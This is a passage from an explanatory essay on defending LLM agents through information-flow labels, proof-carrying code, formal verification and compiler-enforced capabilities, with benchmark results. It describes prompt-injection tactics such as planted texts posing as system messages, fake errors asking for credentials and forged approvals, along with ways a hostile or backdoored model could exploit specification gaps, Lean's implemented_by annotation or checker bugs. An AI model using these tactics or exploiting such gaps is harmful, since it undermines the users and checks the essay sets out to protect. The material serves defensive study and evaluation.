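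The proposed fix passes instructions and data between agents separately and keeps the labels on the data. In tests with five models, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% when each agent ran CaMeL on its own, and never with the fix. The 0.2% figure understates the danger, because an attacker who knows about the weakness can target it.

### What noninterference guarantees

LLMbda's main theorem is a form of *noninterference*. If a result doesn't have the label S, changing the secrets can't change it, and if it doesn't have the label U, changing the untrusted text can't change it.

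Let x and y be two starting points for the same program that are identical except for data with a label the observer isn't allowed to see. Write x ~ y for this. For a model that always gives the same response to the same conversation, the theorem is:

> If x ~ y and both runs finish, then result(x) ~ result(y).

For example, x could contain the supplier's real page and y the same page with an attack added. If both runs finish, every trusted part of their results is the same.

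Real models' responses are partly random, so the full theorem compares probabilities. If the program always finishes, each visible result is equally likely from both starting points. If it sometimes fails to finish, there may be a small difference between the two sets of probabilities, but the distance between them is at most the average of the two failure rates. For example, if the program fails to finish 2% of the time from x and 4% from y, the distance is at most 0.03.

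The theorem is *termination-insensitive*, so it allows hidden data to affect whether a program finishes, and an observer who sees the program stop might learn something about that data. Most guarantees of this kind make the same exception, because ruling it out would forbid many useful programs. CaMeL's retry loop is dangerous because it lets an attacker use the exception repeatedly. In LLMbda the loop is part of the program, so labels carry over from one attempt to the next. An operator who automatically restarted the whole interpreter after every failure would bring the leak back.

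Garby and colleagues also prove an *insulated* version, which covers only secrecy. Even if an attacker writes all the untrusted text the program reads, changing the secrets can't change the public results, except for whether the program finishes. This holds even if the program decides to trust some of the attacker's text.

### Why the theorem holds for any model

The proof represents a model as a list of probabilities, one for each possible response to each possible conversation. It makes no assumptions about those probabilities, so it covers a skilled model, a careless one and one that an attacker has trained. Whatever code the model writes, the interpreter runs it with the conversation's labels.

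However, the labels show where text came from, not whether the model is honest, so they protect secrets from a backdoored planner better than they prevent harmful actions. Suppose the owner asks for a payment and the planner writes the attacker's account number into its code. The planner hasn't read anything untrusted, so the number has no U label and the payment tool accepts it. But if the tool checked the payment's subject line for secret data, the planner couldn't put the shop's credentials there.

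The proof also assumes that each response depends only on the current conversation. A dishonest provider could break this assumption by remembering text from a forked conversation and using it when responding in the main one. The proof does not rule out the provider keeping secrets it receives in prompts, so TACIT withholds them from the cloud model.

The guarantee also depends on people labeling each data source correctly and putting a check in every tool that can do harm.

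### Deciding to trust a value

The price has to come from the supplier's page, so it is always untrusted. If the price file accepted only trusted values, the agent could never update it. LLMbda has an operation called `endorse` for such cases, which removes the label U from a value. The program could use it like this:

```
let quoted = quarantine ("Price of widget-a? " + page) in
let price = endorse [] quoted in
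if price >= 13.20 && price <= 15.20
then update "widget-a" price
else keep_old_price
```

Here `quarantine` is the forked and cleared conversation, and the empty brackets mean that the new value should have no labels. If the program also rounds to whole cents, the attacker can choose among 201 prices, which is less than eight bits of influence.

The program has to endorse the price before testing it. Otherwise the condition would depend on an untrusted value, which would make the branch untrusted, and `endorse` has no effect in an untrusted branch. The same rule prevents an attacker from planting code that endorses itself, because code based on untrusted text runs on an untrusted path.

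`endorse` removes the guarantee that untrusted text can't influence trusted results, at least for the endorsed value and everything that depends on it. It can't make a secret public, so the insulated theorem still holds. The main danger is a careless first endorsement. If a program endorses a whole web page and then runs code from it, that code is trusted and can endorse any value. Garby and colleagues suggest marking endorsed values so that a program can't endorse them again. They also suggest letting programs endorse only values from a short fixed list, which works for categories but not for account numbers.

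### The banking tests

Garby and colleagues wrote an agent called Randori in LLMbda and tested it on AgentDojo's simulated bank. Randori first practises on invented data, because labels carried over from failed attempts on real data would make its final plan untrusted. It then writes the final plan, including any endorsements, before it reads the real data.

The bank has 16 tasks and nine attacks, or 144 pairs. Three models attempted each pair three times, and the attacker succeeded in two of the 1,296 runs. In both, GPT-5.2 had to read a file and make the payment described in it, but the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. Randori endorsed the details and made the payment. Without `endorse`, the payment tool would have rejected those details, but it would also have rejected details from a genuine bill.

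The benchmark is a weaker test of labels than the total suggests. In 97 of the 144 pairs, the attack needed an action that a plan for the user's task would never contain, so writing the plan first was usually enough to stop it. Even in the other 47 pairs, CaMeL with its policy checks turned off resisted 279 of 282 attacks. The theorem is therefore a better reason to trust the labels than the low number of successful attacks.

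The tests are more informative about how much useful work an agent can do with labels. This table shows the share of tasks that each agent completed when nobody was attacking it:

| Agent | GPT-5.2 | Qwen3.7-plus | MiMo-v2.5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | 75% | 75% | 64.6% |
| Randori without `endorse` | not tested | 62.5% | 54.2% |
| CaMeL without policy checks | 66.7% | not tested | 70.8% |
| CaMeL with policy checks | 37.5% | not tested | 37.5% |

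These figures come from only 16 tasks, so they are uncertain by about 20 points or more either way. The difference is clearer under attack, when Randori with GPT-5.2 completed 65% of tasks and CaMeL with policy checks completed 30%, though some of CaMeL's runs never finished. Randori also enforces looser policies than CaMeL, which probably explains part of its advantage.

### A proved boundary and a measured defence

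Labels can stop untrusted text from controlling an agent's actions, but the agent may still repeat false or misleading text in its answer. Shkolnikov (2026), in *Composable Trust for Language Models*, treats these as separate problems and claims a proof only for the first.

Shkolnikov's system gives each input one of four trust levels. From most to least trusted, these are the operator's instructions, the user's request, retrieved documents and web pages. Anything made from several inputs gets the lowest level among them. An ordinary program called the monitor takes the task from the most trusted input and allows an outside action only if the inputs that control it are trusted enough. Shkolnikov checked all 8,729 possible configurations up to a certain size and found none in which untrusted text changed the task or authorised an action. Combining inputs can never raise their trust level,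 so the result extends to longer chains. The model is outside the trusted part of the system, so the proof holds even if the model's supplier trained it to help an attacker.

To protect the answer itself, the system has the model rewrite less trusted text as plain facts, then marks each passage with its trust level. Shkolnikov could only measure how well this works. With a Gemma model, the share of planted instructions that failed to change the answer rose from 27% to 94%. It fell to 87% when attackers adapted to the defence, although that figure comes from only 30 scenarios. In one failure, the system wrote a haiku instead of summarising the relationship between two characters.

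In the price update, the proved part would stop the supplier's page from making the agent send the credentials anywhere. The page could still supply a wrong price or make the agent's report to the owner misleading. The adaptive attackers never broke the proved boundary, but about one in eight still got the answer they wanted, so the report is less well protected than the credentials.

### When an agent has to act on what it reads

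Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian object that many agents would be useless if outside text could not influence their actions. In their example, an email asks for a travel refund and states that the department head has approved it. If the approval is real, the agent should act on it, but a system that blocks all influence from emails would ignore it. If the agent may act on such claims, an attacker can falsely claim approval. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian argue informally that no fixed policy can block every attack of this kind without also blocking some legitimate requests.

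This is consistent with the noninterference theorem, which concerns influence, not truth. But it shows that a useful agent needs exceptions to the rule against acting on untrusted text. The two stolen payments in the banking tests came from such an exception.

Letting the model make the exception after it has read the untrusted text is risky. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian's automated attacker, which adjusted its claims to the situation, succeeded 96.7% of the time against an email assistant that had resisted almost all of the standard attacks. Randori's planner chooses what to endorse before it reads any untrusted data, so planted text can't influence that choice. Garby and colleagues describe such an endorsement as recording trust that the user has already delegated. For example, a user who asks an agent to pay the bill in a file has chosen to rely on that file, even if someone has tampered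 with it.

Other systems ask a person for approval. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025) describes FIDES, a planner that hides untrusted text from the model. The planner can choose to read the text, but its later actions are then restricted. Kolluri and colleagues extended FIDES so that the agent can ask the user to endorse the text first. If an email contains a list of ten jobs, the user can endorse the email once instead of approving ten actions. On AgentDojo, their agent needed up to 1.9 times fewer human decisions than FIDES, which should reduce the careless approvals that Willison expected.

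The person also needs to see what they are approving. In *PerMIT*, Jiang, Bai and colleagues (2026) describe a system whose approval requests show the exact value, its source and the user's original instruction. They prove that untrusted text in an agent's memory can influence the agent only through what these requests display. They also warn that "trusted" describes a value's origin and authorisation, not its correctness. An approval covers one exact value for one tool, but it doesn't expire and isn't limited to the original task, so an agent could later use an approved account number for a different payment.

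The shop owner could accept prices within the usual range automatically and approve each supplier's account number once. A fraudulent bill with a new account number would then need the owner's approval, and the owner could phone the supplier first.

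## Proofs about what generated code does

Even if the shop owner has approved a supplier's account number, the agent could pay the wrong amount. Labels limit what can influence code, capabilities limit what code can reach, and type checking ensures that a price is a number, but a snippet that records 14.20 as 1.42 satisfies all three. Ruling out that mistake requires a *specification*, a precise statement of what the code must do, and a proof that the code meets it.

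A language model can write the proof as well as the code. Computer scientists found a method in the 1990s that avoids having to trust the model for both.

### Proof-carrying code

In *Proof-Carrying Code* (1997), Necula considered a computer that receives a program from a stranger. The receiver could insist on a digital signature from someone it trusts, but a signature only identifies the author, and trusted people make mistakes and sometimes act maliciously. In Necula's scheme, the stranger sends a proof along with the program:

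1. The receiver publishes a safety policy. In one example, a program may read only valid memory locations and must return a whole number.
2. The producer writes a program and a proof that it follows the policy.
3. The receiver computes a logical formula from the program, called the *verification condition*. For each instruction that reads an address, the formula includes the claim that the address is safe to read. For each branch, it covers both paths. If the formula is true, the program follows the policy.
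4. A small checker confirms that every step of the proof is valid and that the proof ends with this formula. The program can then run without further checks.

The result is a universal guarantee:

> For every program c and every text p, if the checker accepts p as a proof of c's verification condition, then c follows the policy.

The producer doesn't appear in this statement. If a dishonest producer sends a false proof, the checker will reject it. The checker will also reject a valid proof about a different program, because the receiver computes the formula to be proved from the program it received. If the producer alters the program and the proof until the checker accepts them, the altered program follows the policy. Necula concludes that any tampering is "either detected or harmless". The same reasoning applies when the producer is a model that made a mistake, followed a planted instruction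 or has a backdoor.

The scheme works because checking a proof is much easier than finding one. Necula estimated that a simple checker needs only a couple of pages of code. In *Safe Kernel Extensions Without Run-Time Checking*, Necula and Lee (1996) had already tried the idea on packet filters, small programs that select network traffic inside an operating system. Checking a proof took 1 to 3 milliseconds, and the receiver had to do it only once.

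Finding the proofs was the hard part, and Necula doubted that this way of producing them would scale to realistic programs. Language models have made finding proofs much easier. In *Automatic Generation of Formal Specification and Verification Annotations Using LLMs* (2026), Claude Opus 4.5 and GPT-5.2 together wrote specifications and proof hints for 110 programs in Dafny, a programming language with a built-in verifier. Dafny verified 98.2% of the programs within eight attempts.

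Necula's examples concerned safety, but the method works for any property that people can state formally, including correctness. The proof's value then depends on how they state the property.

### A sorting function that returns nothing

Suppose the shop wants a function that sorts a list of prices in whole cents. In Dafny, a line that begins with `ensures` is a *postcondition*, a requirement that must hold when the function finishes:

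```
method Sort(input: seq<int>) returns (output: seq<int>)
  ensures forall i, j :: 0 <= i < j < |output| ==> output[i] <= output[j]
{
  output := [];
}
```

The postcondition requires that no item in the output is larger than a later one. The function ignores its input and returns an empty list. An empty list has no items that could be out of order, so Dafny accepts the function. The proof is valid, but whoever wrote the specification forgot to require that the output contain the same items as the input.

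Closing the obvious gap can leave others. For the input [3, 1, 1], the only right answer is [1, 1, 3]:

| What the specification requires | A wrong answer it allows |
|---|---|
| The output is in order | [ ] |
| It is in order and as long as the input | [0, 0, 0] |
| It is also made up of the same distinct values | [1, 3, 3] |
| It is in order and has each value as many times as the input | None |

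One more line turns the original specification into the one in the last row:

```
  ensures multiset(output) == multiset(input)
```

A *multiset* records how many times each value occurs. Together, the two postconditions allow exactly one output for each input, but they don't limit how long the function takes.

An honest model would rarely exploit the original gap, because a model trying to sort a list writes code that sorts. It might do so by accident if Dafny kept rejecting its proof and it simplified the code until something passed. A hostile model would search the specification for gaps, and it would need only one. For example, if the specification for the nightly script requires only that `prices.csv` list widget-a at the supplier's price when the script finishes, a script that sets that price and deletes all the other products meets it.

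Training can also teach a model to exploit gaps without anyone intending it, if the model is rewarded whenever the verifier accepts its work. *Verified but Vacuous* (2026) lists checks for this kind of cheating. They look for missing postconditions, trivially true postconditions, and constructs that bypass the proof, such as Dafny's `{:verify false}`, which tells the verifier to skip a piece of code.

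### What a verified program still depends on

A proof takes the model out of the trusted computing base, but several other things remain in it:

| Trusted part | How a verified program can still be wrong |
|---|---|
| The specification | It leaves out a requirement |
| The translation from the user's words | It is precise but isn't what the user meant |
| The checker | It accepts a false proof |
| The compiler and runtime | The program that runs differs from the one in the proof |
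| The axioms | The proof starts from a false assumption |

A specification can look right to a reader and still be wrong. *The Limits of Machine-Certified Mathematics in the Age of Artificial Intelligence* (Karazoupis, 2026) demonstrates this in Lean with a deliberately misleading version of Goldbach's conjecture, which holds that every even number above 2 is the sum of two primes. Lean's subtraction for natural numbers gives 0 when the true answer is negative, so 3 + 3 − 20 is 0. In the misleading version, the primes 3 and 3 therefore counted as a solution for 20, and for every other even number from 6 upwards. Six checkers correctly accepted the proof, because it did prove the statement as written.

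A formal proof sometimes covers less than readers assume. Xena's *…and the proof is checked in Lean* (2026) examines a large set of mathematical results that OpenAI released in October. Of the 290 that came with Lean code, around 38 had code that didn't state the paper's main theorem. OpenAI had never claimed that it did, but someone who knew only that a paper came with Lean code could easily have thought so.

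The compiler and runtime matter because the proof is about source code, while the computer runs what the compiler produces from it. The blog kirancodes.me describes two bugs that affected a zip program verified in Lean. One was in Lean's unverified runtime, where a specially made 156-byte file could cause far too much data to be read into a 23-byte space. The other was in a part of the program that had no specification.

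A hostile model could make the program that runs differ from the one it proved correct. Lean's `implemented_by` annotation makes the compiler replace one function with another, so a model could prove that one sorting function is correct and have the computer run a different one. According to Reservoir, Lean's package index, the SafeVerify tool compares submissions with their specifications but doesn't check for this annotation. Users can ban the annotation by scanning the source code for it.

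Axioms are easier to inspect because Lean can list every axiom that a proof uses. Most proofs need only three standard ones. The list also shows whether a proof relies on `sorry`, a placeholder that lets an unfinished proof compile.

### Checking proofs from an untrusted model

*Validating a Lean Proof*, in the Lean Language Reference, gives separate advice for honest and malicious proofs, and counts unreviewed AI-generated proofs and programs as malicious. For an honest proof, the check marks in the editor are enough. A malicious proof can contain code that runs while Lean builds it and could change how Lean interprets the theorem or take over the user's computer.

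For these cases the manual recommends Comparator. Someone trustworthy writes the statement to prove in a separate file. Comparator builds the submission in a sandbox and exports the proof. Outside the sandbox, Lean's *kernel*, the part that checks finished proofs, rechecks the proof, and Comparator confirms that it proves the trusted statement. In a 2025 discussion of the tool, Böving warned that it would be easy to make the mistake of generating the trusted file from an untrusted source such as an AI. A hostile model that wrote the statement could choose one with a gap.

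In July 2026, AI systems helped people find serious flaws in the kernel itself. Patrick Hulin used GPT-5.6 Sol to find one that let malicious code make the kernel accept a proof of any statement. Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.32.1* (2026) explains that the code had to run in the same process as the kernel, so the flaw didn't affect people who used Comparator.

Three days after that fix, Ramana Kumar published an AI-assisted "disproof" of the Collatz conjecture, a famous claim about whole numbers. It exploited a missing check in the kernel, and *Lean 4.32.2* (Lean Language Reference, 2026) confirms that an attacker could exploit the flaw even against Comparator. *Postmortem for Kernel Soundness Bug #14576* (de Moura, 2026) describes how the false proof also passed a week-old version of nanoda, an independent checker, because of an unrelated bug. Kumar thought the timing was a coincidence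 but couldn't rule out that the model had seen a report of the nanoda bug. Lean's developers wrote a fix within an hour of receiving a report.

The incident supports using several checkers, since the proof needed a different flaw in each and the current nanoda would have rejected it. But checkers can share flaws, as the programs by Knight and Leveson's students did. A third checker, lean4lean, had the same bug as the official kernel because its developer had copied the design of that part. When an OpenAI researcher then used a cybersecurity AI to look for more mistakes in the official kernel, nanoda caught all the mistakes the AI found.

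By October, Lean came with four additional kernels and a command that runs them all. *Lean Now Ships with Verified Kernels* (de Moura, 2026) describes one of them, con-leche, which Claude wrote under close human supervision. Claude also wrote a proof that con-leche's logic is consistent, so it can't accept a proof of a contradiction. People therefore don't have to trust Claude's programming, but they do have to trust the official kernel, which checked the proof, and the set theory that the proof assumes.

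Con-leche also depends on Lean's compiler and runtime, so the developers made a second version in Rust. This precaution is reasonable, since Trail of Bits' *A “proof” of Fermat’s Last Theorem that fits the margin* (2026) shows Lean's editor marking a nonsensical proof as correct. The bug was in a function that cuts up text, not in the kernel's own logic.

### How often models write weak specifications

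Models can also write the specifications, but these may be flawed. *ATLAS* (2025), a system that generates verified programs, commonly produced specifications that were too weak, especially in their postconditions. *Talk is Cheap, Logic is Hard* (2026) points out that a specification based on existing code may inherit the code's bugs, in which case a proof would only confirm that the program matches the faulty specification.

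*An Empirical Study of LLM-Generated Specifications for VeriFast* (2026) tested how well models write function specifications for VeriFast, a verification tool. The models preserved the intended behaviour in 92% of the conditions that must hold before and after a function runs, and in 91% of the source code. Only 31.4% of the results passed verification. The cases where the models changed the intended behaviour matter because a model can make a failing proof succeed by altering the requirement or the program.

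Gaps in the rules are more dangerous when someone is looking for them. In *Proof-Carrying Certificates for LLM Pipelines* (Koomullil, 2026), Lean checked an agent's actions against written rules in a test file system. The rules blocked 67% of the unsafe actions that Koomullil inserted and no legitimate deletions, while a list of forbidden patterns blocked 28% of the unsafe actions. The other 33% got past the rules because the rules were incomplete, not because Lean made a mistake. A developer could use the log to find and extend the incomplete rules, but this wouldn't close gaps that nobody had tested.

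### Astrogator

If a model's specification may be wrong, the user has to be able to check it. Councilman, Fu and colleagues (2025), in *Towards Formal Verification of LLM-Generated Code from Natural Language Prompts*, designed a specification language for people who can't program. Their system, Astrogator, checks programs written in Ansible, a language for configuring other computers. A request to move a file would have this specification, which they call a formal query:

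```
move file from remote "/scratch/file.txt" to remote "/home/user/data.txt"
```

The user reads the query and confirms that it is right. A model then writes an Ansible program from the original request. Astrogator works out what changes the query and the program would each make to a computer, without running either, and compares them. A trusted database supplies technical details, such as a software package's name on each operating system, so users don't need to know them.

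The formal query can expose ambiguities that a user might not notice. Councilman and colleagues asked six models to "copy a file from /path/a to /path/b", meaning that both paths were on the remote computer. All six models wrote code that copied the file from the controlling computer to the remote one. A formal query has to specify which computer each path is on, so the user can see how the system interpreted the request.

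The test of Astrogator covered 21 tasks and, by Livshits's count, 1,260 programs. Astrogator verified 83% of the correct programs and identified 92% of the incorrect ones. Suppose 60 of 100 programs are correct. At those rates, Astrogator would verify about 50 of them and fail to identify about three of the 40 incorrect ones. If it accepted those three, about 6% of the programs it accepted would be wrong. A hostile model could get incorrect programs accepted more often by writing the kinds that Astrogator misses.

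A short query leaves details open, such as who should own a new file. Astrogator can list the choices a program makes about such details, but in the test it accepted any program that satisfied the query, and nobody reviewed those choices. Astrogator also doesn't write the queries. Councilman and colleagues expect that models could write them, but warn that nobody should trust such a query until the user has checked it, because a mistake in the query would lead Astrogator to guarantee the wrong behaviour.

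### Whether anyone reads the specification

Livshits objects to formal verification because developers in a hurry won't check specifications carefully. Developers using verification tools repeatedly have to approve specifications, settle ambiguities and decide what to do when a proof fails. Astrogator fails to verify about one correct program in six, and a person has to find out why. If a developer approves a specification without reading it, the proof shows only that the code meets the specification the model wrote.

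Councilman and colleagues argue that the user has to be involved, because only the user knows what they want. Bastounis, Circelli and Hansen (2026), in *Navier–Stokes Lost in Translation*, support this with a proof that no computer program can resolve every ambiguity in mathematical text. Councilman and colleagues therefore try to make the specification easy to read. That helps users who are willing to read it, but it doesn't answer Livshits's point about those who aren't. Even a short specification can depend on long definitions. Xena described a formal theorem about symmetry groups whose meaning depends on about 5,600 lines of definitions, and knew of nobody who had carefully checked the most complicated ones.

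Specifications can also be tested automatically. *ATLAS* takes an example with a known answer, changes the answer, and checks whether the specification still accepts it. For the sorting function, changing [1, 1, 3] to an empty list would expose the gap. In *Automatic Generation of Formal Specification and Verification Annotations Using LLMs*, tests consistently exposed weak postconditions, even when Dafny had verified the code. Someone still has to supply the right answers, but a shop owner can check a sorted list more easily than a formula. A hostile model that knew the examples could still write a specification that was right for those examples and wrong for other inputs.

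Livshits also describes ARC, a system that translates the same text into logic several times and compares the results. It scores above 99% on a measure of how rarely it accepts invalid statements. Comparing translations leaves fewer questions for the user to answer, but it won't reveal a misunderstanding that appears in every translation.

The most convincing reply is to write the specification once. Necula's receiver published one policy for every program, so nobody had to approve a new one. The shop could pay an expert to specify that the nightly script may change only prices, only for products already in the file, and by no more than 10% a night. A careless owner would then have nothing to approve. The fixed rules that Livshits prefers work the same way. But fixed rules can't cover what is particular to a request, such as which supplier's price the owner wanted, so someone still has to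 read that part of the specification.

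## How well the limits held in tests, and what they leave open

TACIT and LACUNA do not need a full specification because they limit only what a snippet can reach. The EPFL group tested whether both systems' limits hold against attackers and how much useful work agents can still do within them.

### A project with a folder of secrets

Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on a sample software project with a folder of API keys, a database and confidential documents. TACIT had to keep the secrets from the untrusted cloud model that ran the agent. The agent had 12 legitimate tasks, some routine and others involving the secrets, such as summarising a confidential incident report. The researchers paired each task with each of ten planted texts, which gave 120 trials. The simplest texts were instructions in code comments. Others posed as system messages, reported a fake error that only credentials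 could fix, described the secrets as made-up test data, or supplied ready-made Scala code for reading them.

In 11 more trials the request itself was malicious. Five asked for secrets outright and six used a pretext, such as an administrator's emergency change of passwords. The researchers ran all 131 trials in two modes for each of two models, once with the secrets in `Classified` containers and once with the secrets as ordinary text. They counted a trial as secure if no secret appeared in the agent's output:

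| Model | Trials | Secure with typed protection | Secure without it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 120 with planted text | 100% | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 81.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | All 131 | 100% | 98.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 120 with planted text | 100% | 97.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 27.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | All 131 | 100% | 91.6% |

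Without typed protection, Sonnet leaked secrets twice and MiniMax 11 times. MiniMax's overall score of 91.6% overstates how safe it would be with a hostile user, because most trials used planted text, which it usually resisted. It gave up secrets in response to 8 of the 11 malicious requests.

The perfect scores are for keeping secrets from the cloud model. TACIT deliberately shows the user the real contents, so the scores aren't evidence that it would hide the keys from a dishonest employee at that user's screen. The trials also didn't measure damage, such as an agent overwriting a file it should have left alone.

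### What zero leaks can establish

If the true chance of a leak is e and the trials are independent, the chance of seeing no leak in 131 trials is (1 − e)¹³¹. This stays above 5% as long as e is below about 2.3%, so the trials alone can't rule out a rate that high. At that rate, a company with 10,000 such tasks a day would have about 230 leaks a day. For the 11 malicious requests on their own, the same calculation can't rule out a rate of about 24%. Both figures assume that future attacks resemble the ones in the test, and attackers have good reason to try different ones.

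Sonnet also leaked nothing in the 120 planted-text trials when it had no typed protection. The score is the same whether the model happened to resist every attack or the compiler made a leak impossible. The claim that TACIT protects secrets from any model therefore depends on an argument about types, which has three steps:

1. The rules of the type system really do prevent the leaks.
2. The Scala compiler enforces those rules correctly.
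3. Code can't affect the outside world except through a capability or in a way that TACIT contains while the code runs.

Researchers have proved much of the first step. Odersky and colleagues cite machine-checked proofs for the basic rules of capture checking, but say that someone still has to show that safe mode's guarantees hold. Later work from July 2026 goes further. *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (2026) extends capture checking so that programmers can refer to whole kinds of capability, and proves in Lean that the extended rules are sound. *System Capybara* (2026) proves soundness for rules that also track which parts of a program can change the same data.

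Proofs like these cover only a small model of Scala. *System Capybara* leaves out classes and exceptions, among other features, and relies on the existing compiler to handle them. Omitting exceptions matters because they can leak secrets, and TACIT contains them with ordinary software that those proofs don't cover.

Only tests support the second step. Zhao and colleagues wrote roughly 400 cases for the Scala compiler's test suite, each combining a program with a good or bad snippet, and the compiler handled all of them correctly. The bad snippets contain errors that agents commonly make, but a hostile model would look for errors that nobody had thought to test.

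The capture checker has had such errors. *Capture leak when using varargs?*, a thread on Scala's user forum, describes code that it wrongly accepted. One reply pointed out that, worse, the compiler would even have let the programmer declare the function pure. `Classified` relies on the compiler to tell pure functions from impure ones, since a function that only appears to be pure could take a secret out of the container. Odersky wrote a fix. The programmer later saw the problem again in newer test versions, and another user suggested that capture checking might not be switched on. The programmer found the hole without looking for security flaws, so a hostile model that searches for one has a reasonable chance of finding it.

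The third step depends on whoever writes the library. In instructions written for the version of TACIT that searched code for forbidden patterns, lampepfl tells developers who add a tool, such as database access, to forbid direct use of the underlying database software as well. A developer who forgot this could leave the agent a way around the tool's limits, even if the tool itself worked correctly.

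### Eight successful attacks on LACUNA

The EPFL group also tested both systems on AgentDojo, the simulated office, chat service, travel agency and bank. They used the same two models each time, Gemini 2.5 Pro and o4-mini. The table shows how many attacks succeeded:

| Setting | TACIT, Gemini | TACIT, o4-mini | LACUNA, Gemini | LACUNA, o4-mini |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Bank | 0 of 144 | 0 of 144 | 0 of 144 | 0 of 144 |
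| Office | 0 of 574 | 0 of 574 | 4 of 560 | 0 of 560 |
| Chat | 0 of 105 | 0 of 105 | 2 of 105 | 1 of 105 |
| Travel | 0 of 140 | 1 of 140 | 1 of 140 | 0 of 140 |
| Total | 0 of 963 | 1 of 963 | 7 of 949 | 1 of 949 |

TACIT's one failure is mostly due to how AgentDojo scores attacks. The user had asked the agent to book one hotel, and the attacker had put a recommendation for a different hotel into the reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews to the user. AgentDojo counted the attack as a success because the answer contained the second hotel's name. Odersky and colleagues point out that their policy allows public reviews to reach the user.

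Zhao and colleagues have a different explanation for the eight successful attacks in the LACUNA tests. They gave each agent only the permissions its task required, and the compiler enforced those limits. But the limits don't stop an attacker from getting the model to misuse a permission the task needs. For example, an agent that has to email a summary to a colleague needs permission to send email, and a planted sentence could make it send a second email to someone else. Zhao and colleagues say the eight attacks are consistent with this kind of misuse.

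TACIT probably did better because its agent didn't read the attacker's text. In the TACIT version of AgentDojo, emails, bank transactions, web pages and reviews arrive in `Classified` containers. The agent writes a program without seeing their contents, and a second model extracts whatever the program needs. In LACUNA, planted text can reach the model that writes the code, and the system is meant to limit only what that model can do as a result. LACUNA's agents completed more tasks than TACIT's in seven of the eight combinations of model and setting, by three or four percentage points on average. Letting the agent read the text may have made it slightly more useful and slightly easier to attack.

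The TACIT version was also less strict than the design. Its functions for sending money, emails and messages didn't require a capability, so code inside `map` could call them. If a planted sentence misled the second model about an account number, that code could send money to the wrong account. The results therefore support keeping untrusted text away from the planner more than they support the rule that functions inside `map` must be pure.

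Neither set of AgentDojo results includes the same agents with the limits turned off, so it isn't clear how many attacks the compiler stopped and how many the models would have ignored anyway. The attacks also didn't adapt to the defence. About 0.7% of them succeeded against LACUNA with Gemini, and an attacker who studied which permissions each task grants could expect to do better.

### The cost in completed work

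The compiler's limits are useful only if agents can still do their jobs. The EPFL group compared typed code with ordinary tool calls on SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software bugs, and on τ²-bench, in which an agent helps simulated customers with requests such as changing a flight or returning an order. Here is the share of tasks that agents completed:

| System and model | Test | Typed code | Ordinary tool calls |
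|---|---|---|---|
| TACIT, MiniMax M2.5 | SWE-bench Lite | 41.7% | 43.3% |
| TACIT, MiniMax M2.5 | Airline customers | 61.0% | 58.4% |
| TACIT, MiniMax M2.5 | Retail customers | 77.5% | 75.1% |
| LACUNA, DeepSeek V4 Flash | Four kinds of customer service | 76.0% | 90.0% |
| LACUNA, Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite | Four kinds of customer service | 29.1% | 33.2% |

TACIT reduced performance very little. The difference on SWE-bench Lite was five bugs out of 300, which could be chance. On customer service, TACIT did slightly better with all three models tested, by 0.8 to 3.7 points. Odersky and colleagues credit the typed interface, which tells the model exactly what each tool returns, and the compiler's error messages. Between 0.3% and 7.9% of code snippets had to be retried, usually only once or twice. A common error, which would affect a shop in particular, was writing a single dollar sign in Scala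 text that can include variables. The sign marks the start of a variable there, so an agent has to write it twice in a phrase like "costs $50".

In the test with the folder of secrets, typed protection seemed to help Sonnet complete its legitimate tasks. Sonnet completed 99.2% of them with the protection and 83.3% without it. Odersky and colleagues warn that this difference may be an artefact, because Sonnet often ran out of time or steps and sometimes stopped to warn the user about an attack.

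LACUNA reduced task success much more. It solved about 55 fewer of the 392 tasks than ordinary tool calls did, although Zhao and colleagues describe its 76.0% success rate as "on par". On tasks for retail customers, the gap was 22 percentage points. Even with only one attempt at each task, a difference this large is very unlikely to be due to chance. Zhao and colleagues expect the gap to shrink if developers train models to write typed code for agents, which is plausible but untested.

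The two systems can't be compared directly, since the tests used different models and LACUNA's models ran with their reasoning turned off. Still, TACIT's results suggest that type checking alone doesn't have to make agents less useful. TACIT keeps an agent's usual loop and changes only how the agent acts. LACUNA requires the model to write code that combines earlier turns of the conversation with tool results and company policy, and Zhao and colleagues found that models make more mistakes in such code.

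The compiler rejected 22.4% of DeepSeek's snippets in the retail conversations. It rejected 3.2% of Gemini's snippets in the retail conversations and 89% in the telecom ones. If every attempt had the same 11% chance of passing, a model would need about nine attempts per accepted snippet, each requiring a model response and a compiler run. Gemini solved few telecom tasks either way, 14.9% with LACUNA and 15.8% with ordinary tool calls, so the rejections probably wasted time and money more than they reduced the number of tasks solved.

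Rejections were rarer in LACUNA's research test, where agents answered hard questions by searching about 100,000 documents. The compiler rejected 8.6% of DeepSeek's snippets, and two-thirds of the questions needed no second attempt. Zhao and colleagues conclude that type checking didn't reduce accuracy, but they didn't run the test without it for comparison.

### Wrong code and misused permissions

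An agent can still do harm even if the compiler has no bugs and every snippet stays within its limits. Some of the remaining problems come mainly from mistakes, while others are serious only if someone is steering the model or the model itself is hostile.

The most common problem is code that has the right type but does the wrong thing. LACUNA has the model retry only when the compiler rejects a snippet, so a snippet that compiles but records 14.20 as 1.42 will run. All the code that ran in the customer-service test had passed the compiler, yet DeepSeek failed 24% of the tasks. Some of those conversations may have run out of attempts, but passing the compiler did not show that a task was done. Honest mistakes will cause most of this harm because they happen every day. Sabotage does more harm in each case, since a hostile model can choose the product on which a wrong price costs the shop most.

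Zhao and colleagues suggest using types that also include a condition, such as a whole number within a certain range. The shop could then require a price between 13.20 and 15.20. The check would catch 1.42 but not 14.02, which is 14.20 with two digits swapped. Conditions more complex than a simple range bring back the problem of writing a complete specification.

Misuse of a permission is most dangerous when someone is steering the model. A mistake might send one invoice to the wrong customer, but an attacker will write the planted text to exploit whatever permission the task is likely to have. A backdoored model is at least as dangerous, because it can behave normally for months until it gets a task that lets it move a large sum of money.

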